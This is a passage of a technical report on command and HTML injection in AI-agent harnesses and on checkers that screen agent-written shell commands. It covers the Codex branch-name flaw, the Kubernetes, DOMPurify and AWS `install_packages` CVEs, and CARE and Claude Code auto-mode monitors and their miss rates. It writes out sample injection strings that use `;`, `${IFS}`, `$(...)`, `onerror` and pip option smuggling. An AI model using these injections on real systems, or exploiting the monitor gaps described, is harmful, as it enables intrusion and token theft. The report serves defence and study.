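When a harness deletes apostrophes to block attacks, it also deletes them from names like O'Brien, because the filter can't distinguish the two uses. Nobody can recover the original name from the result, since O'Brien and OBrien both become OBrien. A database that identifies customers by name may then treat two people as the same customer.

Stripping characters harms coding agents more than most, because their normal output is full of special characters. Without its angle brackets and ampersands, `if (a < b && c > d)` is no longer code. A filter that deletes anything resembling an HTML tag turns "if a<b and c>d" into "if ad". The worst deletions leave a sentence that still makes sense. For example, a harness that deletes exclamation marks to protect an interactive Bash session changes "exit code != 0" to "exit code = 0", making a failed build look successful.

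Some functions strip characters even though their names suggest escaping. On Windows, PHP's `escapeshellarg` replaces each double quotation mark with a space, as Tsai and Splitline mention. The message `test "login" failed` loses its quotation marks, and a file name that ends up with doubled spaces may not match any file.

### Where filtering characters works

Some values have a narrow format, and for these a list of permitted characters works well. A Git commit is usually identified by 40 hexadecimal digits, which Python can check in one line:

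```
re.fullmatch('[0-9a-f]{40}', value)
```

None of the permitted characters can end a quotation or start a command in any of the interpreters discussed here, and best-fit conversion leaves them all unchanged. The developer doesn't need to know every dangerous character, because the check rejects anything unlisted. The details of the check matter, because `re.match` with a dollar sign at the end of the pattern would accept a line break after the digits, and `\d` accepts digits from other scripts as well as 0 to 9.

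The harness should reject a bad value instead of deleting the characters that don't belong. If it expects a task number and the agent writes "12 of 30", deleting everything except digits produces task 1230.

Formats that permit more characters need more care. A list of allowed characters for branch names would normally include the hyphen, which lets `--help` through as an option, so the check should also require the name to start with a letter or digit. This check will reject some legal branch names, since Git permits semicolons and dollar signs, but few projects need those. There is no reasonable list for people's names or status messages.

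Terminal control characters, which have no escaped form, are the other case where removal works well. They are single characters in a fixed range, so deleting them can't create new ones. Deleting whole colour codes can create new codes, because when one code sits inside another, removing the inner code joins the remaining parts of the outer one.

### HTML sanitisers

Agents often write formatted text. If a progress page escaped all of it, users would see the tags instead of bold type and lists, so the harness has to keep some tags and remove others. An HTML sanitiser parses the text into a tree of elements, removes everything its rules don't permit, and builds its output from what is left. DOMPurify turns the first of these lines into the second:

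```
<b>done</b><img src="x" onerror="alert('INJECTED')">
<b>done</b><img src="x">
```

The `onerror` attribute holds a script that would run when the image failed to load.

An HTML sanitiser with a list of permitted elements is the strongest form of stripping because it works on parsed elements. The text `<scr<script>ipt>` defeats a filter that deletes `<script>` once, by leaving a new `<script>` behind, but an HTML parser reads its first part as one element named `scr<script`, which is not on the list. Ordinary text also survives, since the sanitiser writes the `<` in "a < b" as `&lt;`.

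However, applications usually take DOMPurify's output as a string and pass it to the browser, which parses it again. HTML's rules are so complicated that the second parse may produce a different tree, in which harmless text has become a live tag. Security researchers call this mutation XSS (cross-site scripting). According to Searchlight Cyber's *Two Bypasses for Chrome's Sanitizer API* (2026), DOMPurify is safe from it for now, having been hardened over many past attacks, but nothing in theory prevents another one.

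Whether a sanitised string is safe also depends on where the application puts it. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-65914* (2026) describes a flaw in DOMPurify versions before 3.3.2, in which sanitised HTML could become dangerous again inside an element such as `noscript` or `iframe`. The library had a pattern meant to catch closing tags hidden in attributes, but NVD's *CVE-2026-0540 Detail* reports that five element names were missing from it. An earlier version of the pattern lacked `textarea`.

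GitLab's page listed 21 DOMPurify advisories for 2026 by late November, two of them explicitly for incomplete earlier fixes. Most of the flaws require a non-default setting or an unusual use of the output, and a library this popular attracts a lot of scrutiny, so the number looks worse than it is. But *The HTML Sanitizer API* (Alfy, 2026) points out that the maintainers also have to keep up with browsers, because a new browser feature can make previously safe HTML dangerous.

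Browser makers have now started to build in a sanitiser of their own. A page can insert a message with one call:

```
status.setHTML(message)
```

With `setHTML`, the browser parses the text, removes what is unsafe and inserts the resulting tree directly, so it never has to parse a string a second time. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* describes this single call as the core of the design. Developers can supply their own list of elements to allow or remove, but `setHTML` removes `<script>` even if their list allows it, according to MDN's *Element*. A separate method, `setHTMLUnsafe`, lacks this protection and removes nothing by default.

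Chrome shipped an earlier version of the Sanitizer API and withdrew it, according to Chromium's *Intent to Ship*. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) announced in February that Firefox 148 was the first browser with the standard version. Chrome 146 added it on 10 March, according to Chrome for Developers' *Chrome 146* (2026). Safari does not support it, according to the table in web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API*, so pages still need DOMPurify as a fallback.

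Chrome 146 shipped with two flaws in the new sanitiser, which Searchlight Cyber explains. One involved SVG, a drawing format in which an animation can change a link's address. The sanitiser removed such animations by comparing the name of the attribute they changed with two fixed strings. Chrome's SVG code also accepted a name with an extra part on the end, so an animation using such a name could get through. Chrome fixed this by making the sanitiser read the name with the SVG code's own parser.

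The other flaw involved addresses that start with `javascript:`, which the sanitiser is supposed to remove. It left malformed ones in place because the browser refuses to open them. But when a user submitted a form with a malformed address, Chrome rebuilt it into a valid one and the script ran. The text had changed after filtering, much as it did in PHP-CGI. Chrome's developers had patched both flaws by 3 March, a week before version 146 came out, but the fixes didn't reach users until version 147 on 7 April.

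Server programs can't call `setHTML`, because it exists only in browsers. Hong, a developer, objects that servers do much of the sanitising and must still use libraries with their own HTML parsers, which may interpret the same HTML differently from the browser. A harness with a progress page can avoid this problem by sending the agent's message to the browser as JSON and calling `setHTML` there. Even then, a sanitiser that permits links will keep one with a harmless-looking label and a malicious destination, because it is valid HTML.

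## Passing data without building a command string

Escaping and filtering both prepare a message to be inserted into text that an interpreter will parse. Developers can often avoid building that text, because operating systems and databases accept a command and its data separately. Developers then don't have to predict how an interpreter will read the message.

### Argument lists on Unix

In Python, the notification becomes:

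```
subprocess.run(['notify-send', 'Agent', message])
```

Python starts a new process and makes a system call named `execve`, which takes the path of a program file, a list of argument strings and a list of environment variables. Each string is a sequence of bytes ending in a null byte. The kernel, the core of the operating system, copies the strings into the new program's memory. It limits their length but doesn't search them for spaces, quotation marks or semicolons. For the message that earlier printed INJECTED, `notify-send` receives this:

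```
argument 0    notify-send
argument 1    Agent
argument 2    done'; echo 'INJECTED
```

No shell is running, so the semicolon doesn't end the command and the apostrophe in "didn't" arrives intact. The harness directly builds C(s), the intended command in the equation for correct escaping, without a template, an escaping function or a parser. Python still raises an error if the message contains a null byte, and Linux rejects any single argument longer than 128 KiB.

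A developer who switches to an argument list has to remove the old escaping. If `shlex.quote` stays in the code, the user sees its quotation marks in the notification. An argument list also gives no protection if one of its items is a command string built from the message:

```
subprocess.run(['sh', '-c', f"notify-send Agent '{message}'"])
```

This starts a shell and gives it the same vulnerable line. `ssh` has a similar effect because it joins its arguments into one string for the remote shell.

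Sometimes the harness does need a shell, for instance to run a second command only if the first succeeds. It can then write the command as fixed text and pass the message to the shell as an argument:

```
subprocess.run(['sh', '-c', 'notify-send Agent "$1" && date >> log.txt',
                'sh', message])
```

The shell parses the fixed text, then replaces `$1` with the message without parsing the result as a command. Without the double quotation marks around `$1`, the shell would split the message at spaces and expand any asterisks. The extra `'sh'` fills `$0`, the name the shell uses in its error messages.

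### Prepared statements in SQL

Databases offer the same separation through prepared statements, in which placeholders stand for the values. With Python's SQLite library, the harness can log a message like this:

```
db.execute('INSERT INTO log (message, failures) VALUES (?, ?)',
           (message, failures))
```

SQLite first parses the text with its question marks and compiles it into a small internal program. The library then binds a value to each question mark, and SQLite runs the program. PostgreSQL does this over a network connection, with separate protocol messages for parsing the statement and binding the values. In both databases, the command's structure is complete before the database uses any value. The message whose backslash and apostrophe added a row in MySQL would simply be stored, since there is no quotation for it to end.

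Prepared statements also protect against injection through numeric inputs, which escaping apostrophes does not. If the online shop had used a placeholder for the card type, the database would have treated `2 OR 1=1` as a single value. PostgreSQL would reject it as an invalid integer, and SQLite would compare it with the stored card types and find no match.

A placeholder can stand only for a value, not for a column name, a table name or a keyword, because the database needs those to compile the statement. If the agent chooses a column, the harness still needs its fixed list of names. A percent sign in a bound `LIKE` pattern keeps its special meaning, because `LIKE` interprets the pattern after binding.

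Some client libraries only imitate prepared statements. With MySQL, for example, PHP's PDO library by default escapes the values itself and inserts them into the query text. The developer's code looks the same, but its safety again depends on correct escaping.

### PowerShell and the Kubernetes flaw

PowerShell separates commands and data through parameter binding. In `Get-Item -LiteralPath $path`, it parses the line, looks up the value of `$path` and passes that value to the parameter named `LiteralPath`. PowerShell doesn't parse the value as code, so a semicolon or `$(…)` in it has no effect. The choice of parameter still matters, because `Get-Item -Path` treats an asterisk in the value as a wildcard.

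A flaw in Kubernetes, a system for running applications in containers across many computers, shows what happens when a developer puts the value into the command instead. On each computer, a program called the kubelet starts the containers. Users can share a folder between a container and its host, and can specify a path within that folder. On Windows, the kubelet used PowerShell to find out whether this path was a link to somewhere else. Datadog Security Labs' *The Kubernetes CVE-2023-3676 Windows command injection vulnerability* (2023) reproduces the line that built the command:

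```
cmd := fmt.Sprintf("(Get-Item -LiteralPath %q).LinkType", path)
```

The kubelet's developers quoted the path with `%q`, which in the Go programming language puts text between double quotation marks and escapes it by Go's rules. PowerShell reads the result as an expandable string, so if the path ends in `$(echo INJECTED)`, PowerShell runs that command before it looks for the file.

The logs that Datadog Security Labs collected indicate that the quoting was wrong even for harmless paths. Go's quoting doubles each backslash, and PowerShell passed both to `Get-Item` as part of the value. Windows ignores surplus backslashes in most paths, so the kubelet kept working.

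In *Can't Be Contained*, Peled (2023) describes how he found the flaw and reported it on 13 July 2023. An attacker needed permission to start containers on the cluster, and could then run commands outside any container, directly on the cluster's Windows computers, as SYSTEM, an account with almost unlimited rights. The flaw had a severity score of 8.8.

The fix, released on 23 August, put the path in an environment variable and left a fixed command:

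```
(Get-Item -LiteralPath $env:linkpath).LinkType
```

The user still chooses the path, but PowerShell now reads it from an environment variable, and only after parsing the command. Peled's statement that the parameters come from environment variables instead of user input is therefore slightly misleading. Two related flaws had the same cause, and ARMO shows that the developers fixed one of them the same way, with a variable named `mountpath`. Kubernetes announced that the patch for the original flaw had no known side effects.

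For administrators who couldn't upgrade, Peled also published a filter rule meant to reject paths that start with `$(`. The condition is inverted, so it matches every path that does *not* start with those characters. Even a corrected version would miss `logs$(echo INJECTED)`. Datadog Security Labs reprint the rule but doubt that anyone could list all the suspicious patterns, and suggest allowing only paths without special characters.

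### Environment variables, standard input and files

A notification harness can use the Kubernetes fix too:

```
subprocess.run(['powershell', '-Command', './notify.ps1 $env:MESSAGE'],
               env={**os.environ, 'MESSAGE': message})
```

The developer should choose the variable's name, because some variables, such as `PATH`, change how programs run. In a POSIX shell, `$MESSAGE` is equally safe inside double quotes. The technique fails in cmd.exe, which inserts the value of `%MESSAGE%` before it parses the line.

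Many programs can also read data from standard input, the stream that a program receives from whatever started it. This suits longer texts, such as the description of a code change:

```
subprocess.run(['git', 'commit', '-F', '-'], input=message, text=True)
```

`-F` makes Git read the description from a file, and the hyphen after it stands for standard input. The harness could also write the description to a file and give Git that file's name. Neither method is subject to the length limit on command-line arguments. The receiving program has to treat its input as data, though, because a shell or `psql` that reads the same text from standard input will run it.

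AppleScript can receive data separately too, which solves the problem that Bolin's repair left in Codex's early notification code. The harness passes the message as an argument:

```
subprocess.run(['osascript',
    '-e', 'on run argv',
    '-e', 'display notification (item 1 of argv) with title "Agent"',
    '-e', 'end run',
    '--', message])
```

AppleScript compiles the three fixed lines, which read the message from the list `argv`. The two hyphens near the end stop `osascript` from treating a message that starts with a hyphen as an option.

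### The branch name in Codex

The cloud version of Codex runs each task in a container, which first downloads the user's code from GitHub. The container logs in with a token, a temporary password that lets it act as the user. Tyler Jespersen of BeyondTrust's Phantom Labs found that the Git branch name reached the container's shell without proper sanitising. In the report quoted by The Hacker News (2026), he says the flaw made it possible to steal the token.

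Suppose the container runs `git checkout BRANCH`, and the branch has this name:

```
main;echo${IFS}INJECTED
```

Git doesn't allow spaces in branch names, but it does allow semicolons, dollar signs and curly brackets, so a branch name can contain `${IFS}` in place of a space. `IFS` is a shell variable that normally contains a space, a tab and a line break. The shell replaces `${IFS}` with these characters, splits the text there and runs `echo INJECTED` after the checkout.

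SC Media's *OpenAI fixes Codex flaw that could lead to GitHub token theft* describes how the researchers hid such a name from the user. They added 94 ideographic spaces (wide blank characters from East Asian text) so that the Codex interface showed only "main". They ended the name with `|| true` to suppress the error the spaces would otherwise cause in Bash.

An attacker who could create branches in a shared repository could therefore target everyone who used Codex on it. Making the malicious branch the default increased the chance that someone would run Codex on that branch. The researchers also triggered the flaw by mentioning `@codex` in a comment on a proposed code change, which started a review container with a different GitHub token.

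BeyondTrust reported the flaw on 16 December 2025, and OpenAI rated it critical. According to SC Media, OpenAI made its first fixes within a week and finished correcting the shell escaping in January. The Hacker News reports that the flaw was patched as of 5 February 2026. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI Codex vulnerability enabled GitHub token theft via command injection, report finds* (2026) lists better input validation, stronger shell escaping, and limits on what the tokens could do and how long they lasted among the fixes.

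The mention of shell escaping suggests that a shell still parses the branch name. An argument list would have removed this risk:

```
subprocess.run(['git', 'checkout', branch])
```

In *When a Git Branch Name Becomes a Weapon*, Antunovic recommends making this call after checking that the name contains only unaccented letters, digits, hyphens, slashes, underscores and full stops. The check stops command injection, but it accepts the name `-f`, and `git checkout -f` discards the user's uncommitted changes.

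### Typed tool arguments

A tool's description usually includes a schema, which specifies the fields in a tool call and the type of each. This schema would suit a notification tool:

```
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "message": {"type": "string", "maxLength": 200},
    "urgency": {"enum": ["low", "normal", "critical"]}
  },
  "required": ["message", "urgency"],
  "additionalProperties": false
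}
```

If the harness enforces the schema, the agent can't add a third field or put a number where the message belongs. `urgency` is safe to use because the developer wrote all three of its possible values. `message` can still contain any text of up to 200 characters, including every payload discussed so far.

A schema can also require a string to match a pattern, but the pattern may be too loose. One example is `install_packages()`, a function in the toolkit for building agents from AWS, Amazon's cloud division. The function takes a list of Python package names, puts them into a `pip install` command (pip is Python's package installer) and sends the command to a sandbox, where a shell runs it. *A Package Name Was All It Took* (Smith, 2026) describes three successive versions of the function.

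The first version rejected names containing a semicolon, ampersand, pipe, backquote or dollar sign. But it allowed line breaks, so a name could include a second command on a second line.

In April 2026, AWS replaced the list of forbidden characters with a pattern for valid package names. A package name can end with optional extras in square brackets, as in `pandas[performance]`, and the pattern accepted almost anything between the brackets. The name `pandas[$(echo INJECTED)]` therefore matched, and the shell ran `echo INJECTED` before starting pip.

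The third version, in July, quotes each name for the shell and uses a stricter pattern. Quoting stops the shell attacks, including any that the pattern still misses. An argument list would also have stopped them if the sandbox had a way to start pip without a shell.

AWS's *CVE-2026-16796* (2026) advises developers who can't upgrade not to pass "untrusted or model-generated input" to the function. The advice is sound, but it leaves little use for a function meant to let agents install packages. As an alternative, the advisory suggests checking names against the strict rules of PyPI, the public package index, and allowing only comma-separated identifiers between the brackets.

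### Template strings

Developers keep building command strings partly because they are easy to write. A Python f-string such as `f"notify-send Agent '{message}'"` inserts the message and returns an ordinary string with no record of where the message starts or ends, so a function that receives the string later cannot reliably escape the message.

Baker, van Rossum and colleagues (2024), in *PEP 750*, proposed template strings to solve this problem. (A PEP is a design document for a change to Python.) A template string looks like an f-string but starts with a `t`:

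```
template = t"notify-send Agent {message}"
```

The result is a `Template` object, which holds the fixed parts in its `strings` attribute and the message in its `values` attribute. A database library could join the fixed parts with placeholders and send the values separately, while an HTML library could escape each value as it builds the page. Python doesn't allow ordinary text to be added to a template, because the text could be either a fixed part or a value. Template strings have been part of Python since version 3.14.

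A template string does not escape anything. Its safety depends on the function that processes it, and *PEP 750* includes an example that joins all the parts unescaped, as an f-string would.

Python's functions for starting programs don't yet support template strings. *PEP 787* (Humrich and Coghlan, 2025) proposed that `subprocess.run` accept them. Without a shell, `subprocess.run(t"notify-send Agent {message}")` would produce the same argument list as the safe form above. If the call used a shell, Python would apply `shlex.quote` to each value.

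The sample code for the shell version contains a mistake. It quotes each value and then combines the parts with `shlex.join`, which quotes the values a second time and also quotes the fixed parts. For the template `t"cat {filename}"`, the shell would look for a program whose name is `cat` followed by a space.

The proposal is deferred. Humrich and Coghlan decided to develop the idea first as an experimental library, which might make complicated commands as easy to write without a shell as with one. A participant in the forum thread *PEP 787* also noted that Python would have to split the fixed text into arguments by Unix rules, which may surprise Windows users.

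### Argument injection

An argument list doesn't prevent argument injection, because most command-line programs still treat an argument that starts with a hyphen as an option. Suppose an agent reports that three fewer tests failed than the day before:

```
['notify-send', 'Agent', '-3 failures since yesterday']
```

`notify-send` treats `-3` as an unknown option and prints an error, so the user gets no notification. An attacker could use the message `--expire-time=1`, a valid option that produces an empty notification with a requested display time of one millisecond.

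Other programs have more dangerous options. AWS's *CVE-2026-12530* (2026), a notice about the first version of `install_packages()`, treats options as the most serious part of the flaw. Even with shell quoting, a "package name" that started with `--index-url` could make pip download packages from an attacker's server, and one that started with `-r` could expose files in the sandbox.

Many programs accept two hyphens as an end-of-options marker, and treat everything after it as ordinary values. The complete notification is therefore:

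```
subprocess.run(['notify-send', '--', 'Agent', message])
```

The marker doesn't work everywhere. In `git checkout -- main`, Git treats `main` as a file because of the hyphens, so it restores that file instead of switching branches. A format check is better for branch names. Git doesn't let users create a branch whose name starts with a hyphen, so a harness can reject such names without excluding anything useful.

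The developer can also put fixed text in front of the value. In `'--message=' + message`, the argument always starts with the same option, and Git reads the rest as that option's value. For a file in the current folder, the developer can put `./` in front of the name, so that `-f` becomes `./-f`, which can only be a path.

When only a few values make sense, the developer should list them all, as the schema does for `urgency`. AWS recommended a fixed list of approved package names as a workaround for the first flaw. The list also stops an agent from installing a malicious package that has a valid name.

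PowerShell's own commands and scripts largely avoid argument injection. PowerShell identifies parameter names when it parses the line, so it treats a variable containing `-Recurse` as a value rather than a parameter name. This protection does not extend to external programs, which parse their arguments for options themselves.

### Windows

On Windows, Python has to join an argument list into a single command line, so it still builds the command string that the developer avoided writing. Humrich and Coghlan therefore overstate the protection when they describe an argument list as safe on all platforms.

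This usually works, because Python and most programs follow the same convention. It fails if the program is a batch file, because cmd.exe then parses the command line (the BatBadBut problem), or if the program converts its command line to an old code page, as in WorstFit. Some programs also split their command line by their own rules.

A harness can keep the message out of the command line by sending it through standard input:

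```
subprocess.run(['notify.exe'], input=message.encode('utf-8'))
```

The command line then contains only the program's name, and Windows passes the message's bytes unchanged. `notify.exe` has to read UTF-8 from standard input, so this works best for programs that the harness's developers control.

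## Checking commands that the agent writes itself

A coding agent that calls the Bash tool writes the whole command, so the harness has no inserted value to escape and no intended command to preserve. It can only use a command checker, a program that reads the command and decides whether to run it. A command checker has two problems that an escaping function doesn't: the shell changes the text after the check, and no program can work out the effects of every other program.

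### The shell rewrites the text after the check

Suppose an agent wants to list the Python files in a project folder:

```
ls ~/$PROJECT/*.py
```

GNU's *3.5 Shell Expansions* gives the order in which Bash rewrites such a line. Bash first replaces `~` with the user's home folder and `$PROJECT` with the value of that variable. If the value contains a space, Bash splits the result into two words. It then replaces the pattern with the names of the matching files, and finally removes any quotation marks. `ls` may receive one argument or several hundred, and none of them need appear in the text the agent wrote.

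*Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell* (2019) models shell expansion as a machine with seven states that turns each word into a list of strings. A checker that searches the agent's text for forbidden names therefore examines different strings from the ones the shell will use. The checker can't always expand the text first, because expansion includes command substitution, which may require running part of the command. Files and variables can also change between the check and the run.

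A June 2026 survey by the security company Adversa AI found gaps in how ten of eleven agents guard against dangerous commands (Paganini, 2026, *GuardFall Flaw Hits 10 of 11 Popular Open-Source AI Agents*).

### What no checker can decide

Even a perfect model of the shell would leave the second problem. Imagine a checker that could tell, for every command, whether running it would ever print the word INJECTED. Take any program `task.py` that only computes something, and give the checker this command:

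```
python3 task.py > /dev/null; echo INJECTED
```

The shell discards the program's output and reaches `echo` only if the program finishes. The checker would therefore have to determine whether `task.py` ever finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do this for every program, so the checker can't exist. The same argument applies to a command that deletes a file or sends an email.

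Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider's *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* defines static analysis as accepting or rejecting a program in finite time before it runs. The security policies that static analysis can enforce exactly are the decidable ones, meaning those for which some procedure always gives a correct yes or no. One example of an undecidable policy is that a program must never write to the boot sector, the part of a disk that starts the computer. A checker can watch for such a write while the program runs, but it can't predict for every program whether one will happen.

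The result limits practical checks less than it seems to. It concerns all programs, whereas most commands that agents write are short. It doesn't apply to questions about the text alone, such as whether a command contains a semicolon. The proof also depends on programs that can run forever, and a harness that stops every command after ten minutes rules those out.

Hamlen and colleagues say enforcement can fail either because the mechanism lacks computing power or because it can't observe something it needs. Missing information is usually the bigger obstacle. The effect of `make test` depends on a file in the project, which the agent may have just edited. A command that downloads data and acts on it depends on a reply the server hasn't sent yet.

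### Refusing what the checker cannot analyse

A checker can give a guarantee without judging every command correctly. It can accept only the commands it can fully analyse and refuse the rest. Such a checker is sound if it never accepts a command that breaks the policy, even if it refuses many harmless ones.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) applies this idea to skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts for agents. Each skill declares what its scripts may do. Write E(p) for the set of effects that script p can really have, and D for the declared effects. The checker can't always compute E(p), so it computes a larger set Ê(p) that is certain to contain it, and accepts the script only if

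```
Ê(p) ⊆ D
```

A script's actual effects, E(p), all lie inside the checker's estimate, Ê(p), so every accepted script stays within its declaration. To find Ê(p), the checker runs the script on summaries instead of real values. A file path becomes a pattern that covers all the paths it might be, and a number becomes a range. Vague summaries make Ê(p) large, and the checker then refuses harmless scripts. If it assumes that any script might do anything, it is still sound but too strict to be useful.

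Codex uses a simple version of this approach. According to OpenAI's *Rules*, users can write rules that allow, forbid or ask about commands that begin with certain words, and these rules control what Codex may run outside its sandbox. If a shell script consists only of plain words joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `|`, Codex splits it into separate commands and applies the strictest decision that any of them receives. A rule that allows `git add` therefore doesn't allow all of this line:

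```
git add . && echo INJECTED
```

If the script contains a variable, a wildcard, a redirection or a substitution, Codex treats the whole script as a single argument to `bash` instead of trying to interpret it, so rules for the individual commands inside it don't match. When a rule for `git add` does match, the shell therefore has no variables or patterns to expand, and Codex can determine the program's arguments.

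The drawback is that even `ls *.py`, the first command in this report, is refused, because the asterisk stops a rule that allows `ls` from matching. Users who tire of such refusals may write broader rules. Claude Code has its own allow-rules, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026, 49.5 percent of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands. They include 5 percent who allowed any shell command, and another 43 percent with rules for interpreters such as Python, which allow almost as much.

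Codex's guarantee also covers only which programs start and with what arguments. A rule that allows `make test` still allows any commands that the project's Makefile runs for `test`. To judge a command's effects, a checker needs a description of how each program it accepts behaves.

### Checkers that look for mistakes

Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues wrote such descriptions for a tool called SaSh in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*. They chose not to make the tool sound, which means it can miss some dangerous scripts. They argue that almost any script is dangerous in some strange environment, so a tool that considered every environment would warn about most uses of `rm`, the command that deletes files. SaSh instead assumes that commands mostly work as intended and looks for scripts that do damage anyway.

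The main example for SaSh is the 2015 updater for the game store Steam, which was supposed to empty its own folder. When the variable holding the folder's name was empty, the path pointed to the top of the file system, and the updater deleted every file the user could write to. The two lines responsible were 342 lines apart. SaSh finds the fault in 4.8 seconds by simulating the script with symbols in place of unknown values.

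SaSh found 115 of the 116 known bugs in 61 faulty scripts and raised no false alarms on the corrected versions. ShellCheck, the standard tool for finding mistakes in shell scripts, found 42. These are excellent results for catching an agent's accidental errors, but they are little evidence of how well SaSh would work against an attacker, who can choose exactly the conditions that SaSh assumes won't occur.

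Other tools check only whether a command is valid. Althoubi (2026), in *Look Before You Leap*, tested one on 9,930 commands for 482 programs. It caught 95.8 percent of the invalid commands and wrongly flagged 10.0 percent of the valid ones. Checking the syntax and whether the program existed caught half of the errors with no false alarms. All the false alarms came from checking options against the programs' help texts, which are often incomplete. A checker like this saves an agent from wasted attempts, but it doesn't stop valid commands that do harm, such as one that wipes a disk.

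### CARE

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a checker for harmful commands. The checker receives one command at a time, with the location of the project, the user's home folder and some information about files. It doesn't receive the user's request or the conversation.

CARE first canonicalises the command, rewriting it in a standard form so that different spellings of the same command look alike. It does this without running anything, and it keeps the original text. The rewriting follows fixed rules and isn't meant to work out everything the shell would do.

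A parser then turns the result into a syntax tree. If parsing fails and the text contains a high-risk word, CARE blocks the command. Otherwise it gives the command four scores between 0 and 1:

- The program score comes from a list of about 250 programs. Reading a file scores 0, and wiping a disk scores 1.
- The path score depends on which files the command touches and how. Reading an ordinary system file scores 0.10 and writing to it 0.70, while any access to stored passwords or keys scores at least 0.85.
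- The pattern score comes from 139 rules for known dangerous combinations, most of them based on public catalogues of attack methods.
- The structure score reflects syntax that often accompanies attacks, such as feeding text straight into another interpreter.

CARE adds them up with fixed weights:

```
score = 0.3 × program + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure
```

CARE allows a command that scores below 0.15 and blocks one that scores 0.35 or more. Scores in between produce a warning. If a warning rests on strong evidence, such as access to a secret file, CARE blocks the command at once. It sends the remaining unclear cases to a language model, with instructions to block when in doubt.

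Liu and colleagues give the example of a developer copying a finished build to another computer:

```
rsync -avz ./build/ admin@gpu01:/data/
```

The program score is 0.40 because `rsync` uses the network, and the pattern score is 0.75 because one rule covers copying between computers. The other two scores are zero. The total is 0.345, just below the threshold for an outright block, so the command goes to the model, which allows it.

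The main test had 220 dangerous and 329 safe commands. CARE's results were:

| | Blocked | Allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Dangerous commands | 167 | 53 |
| Safe commands | 3 | 326 |

Recall is the share of dangerous commands that a checker blocks, here 167 of 220, or 75.91 percent. Precision is the share of blocked commands that really were dangerous, here 167 of 170, or about 98.2 percent. The false-positive rate is the share of safe commands that the checker blocks, here 3 of 329, or 0.91 percent. F1 combines precision and recall in one number, which is high only if both are:

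```
F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall) = 85.64%
```

Liu and colleagues compared CARE with other checkers on the same commands. The last column below comes from a separate test, in which a language model wrote 600 commands in response to harmful requests and the researchers ran them in a sandbox. Harm is the share of those commands that passed the checker and ran successfully.

| Checker | Recall | False positives | F1 | Mean time | Harm |
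|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0 ms | 74.83% |
| Best of the other static rule sets | 57.27% | 0.30% | 72.62% | 0.02 ms | 55.50% |
| Language model judging every command | 67.27% | 11.25% | 73.09% | 45.90 ms | 51.33% |
| Granite Guardian, IBM's safety model | 82.27% | 45.90% | 65.58% | 17.25 ms | 26.33% |
| CARE without its model | 75.91% | 1.82% | 84.99% | 0.34 ms | 37.33% |
| Full CARE | 75.91% | 0.91% | 85.64% | 2.32 ms | 52.50% |

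The static scores determined the outcome for nearly all commands in the main test. Only 23 of the 549 commands reached the model, which changed the outcome for three, all harmless uses of `rsync`. Most of the static part's success comes from information about particular programs. Removing the program score lowered F1 from 84.99 to 58.31 percent, while removing the syntax tree lowered it only to 83.20 percent.

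In the harm test, CARE performed worse with the model than without it. Full CARE let 52.50 percent of the commands through to a successful run, hardly better than the simpler static rules, while the version without a model let through 37.33 percent. The model had approved commands that the static scores had flagged. Liu and colleagues plausibly suggest that this happened because the same model, Qwen3-Coder-30B, had written the commands. They caution that a successful run in their sandbox is only a rough measure of harm, useful for comparing checkers.

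CARE interferes little with ordinary work. An agent solved 57.00 percent of 300 everyday tasks with full CARE and 57.33 percent without any checker. The false-positive rate was 0.91 percent on one collection of harmless commands, but full CARE blocked between 8 and 13 percent of the commands in other collections.

Precision also depends on how common dangerous commands are. They made up 40 percent of the main test, but an honest user's agent should produce far fewer. Liu and colleagues calculate that if 1 command in 100 were dangerous, then out of 10,000 commands CARE would stop about 76 dangerous ones, miss 24 and block about 90 safe ones. Fewer than half of the blocked commands would be dangerous.

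CARE isn't sound, because it lets through some commands that it can't analyse. A program missing from its list gets a program score of 0.35, which adds 0.105 to the total. Without other evidence, the total stays below the warning threshold of 0.15, so CARE allows the command. Lowering the threshold to 0.10 in the version without a model raised recall from 75.91 to 96.82 percent, but also raised the share of safe commands it blocked from 1.82 to 23.10 percent. Unlisted programs probably account for part of both increases.

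Liu and colleagues say that CARE only partly reduces risk. It checks each command separately, so it can miss a harmful sequence of harmless-looking commands. They recommend using it with a sandbox.

### Judging what the user wanted

A command can be harmful simply because the user didn't ask for it. For example, deleting old branches is routine if the user requested it, but seriously harmful if the agent misunderstood. CARE can't distinguish these cases because it doesn't have access to the user's request.

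Claude Code's auto mode uses a language model to check the agent's commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the model receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. The agent therefore can't argue for a bad command, and hostile text from a web page doesn't reach the model directly. A quick first check either allows or flags each command, and a slower check reconsiders the flagged ones.

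The two checks together wrongly blocked 0.4 percent of 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's staff. They missed 17 percent of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions, though with so few cases, each one changes the result by about two percentage points. The first check alone missed 6.6 percent but blocked 8.5 percent of the harmless calls. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having agreed to it.

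The usual alternative is to ask the user, but people are poor checkers too. In a later study, Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work with a coding agent and replaced one approval request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6 percent of the time, while auto mode blocked 89 percent of the same commands. Their refusal rate fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more requests. The testers weren't working on their own projects and may have cared less about the outcome than real users would, but that alone is unlikely to explain such a large gap between them and auto mode. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems.

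### PandasAI

PandasAI is a Python library that answers questions about data, such as "Which are the top five countries by sales?" A language model writes a Python program to answer the question, and the library runs it. PandasAI filtered the generated code before running it, but NVIDIA's *How Code Execution Drives Key Risks in Agentic AI Systems* describes how the filter failed.

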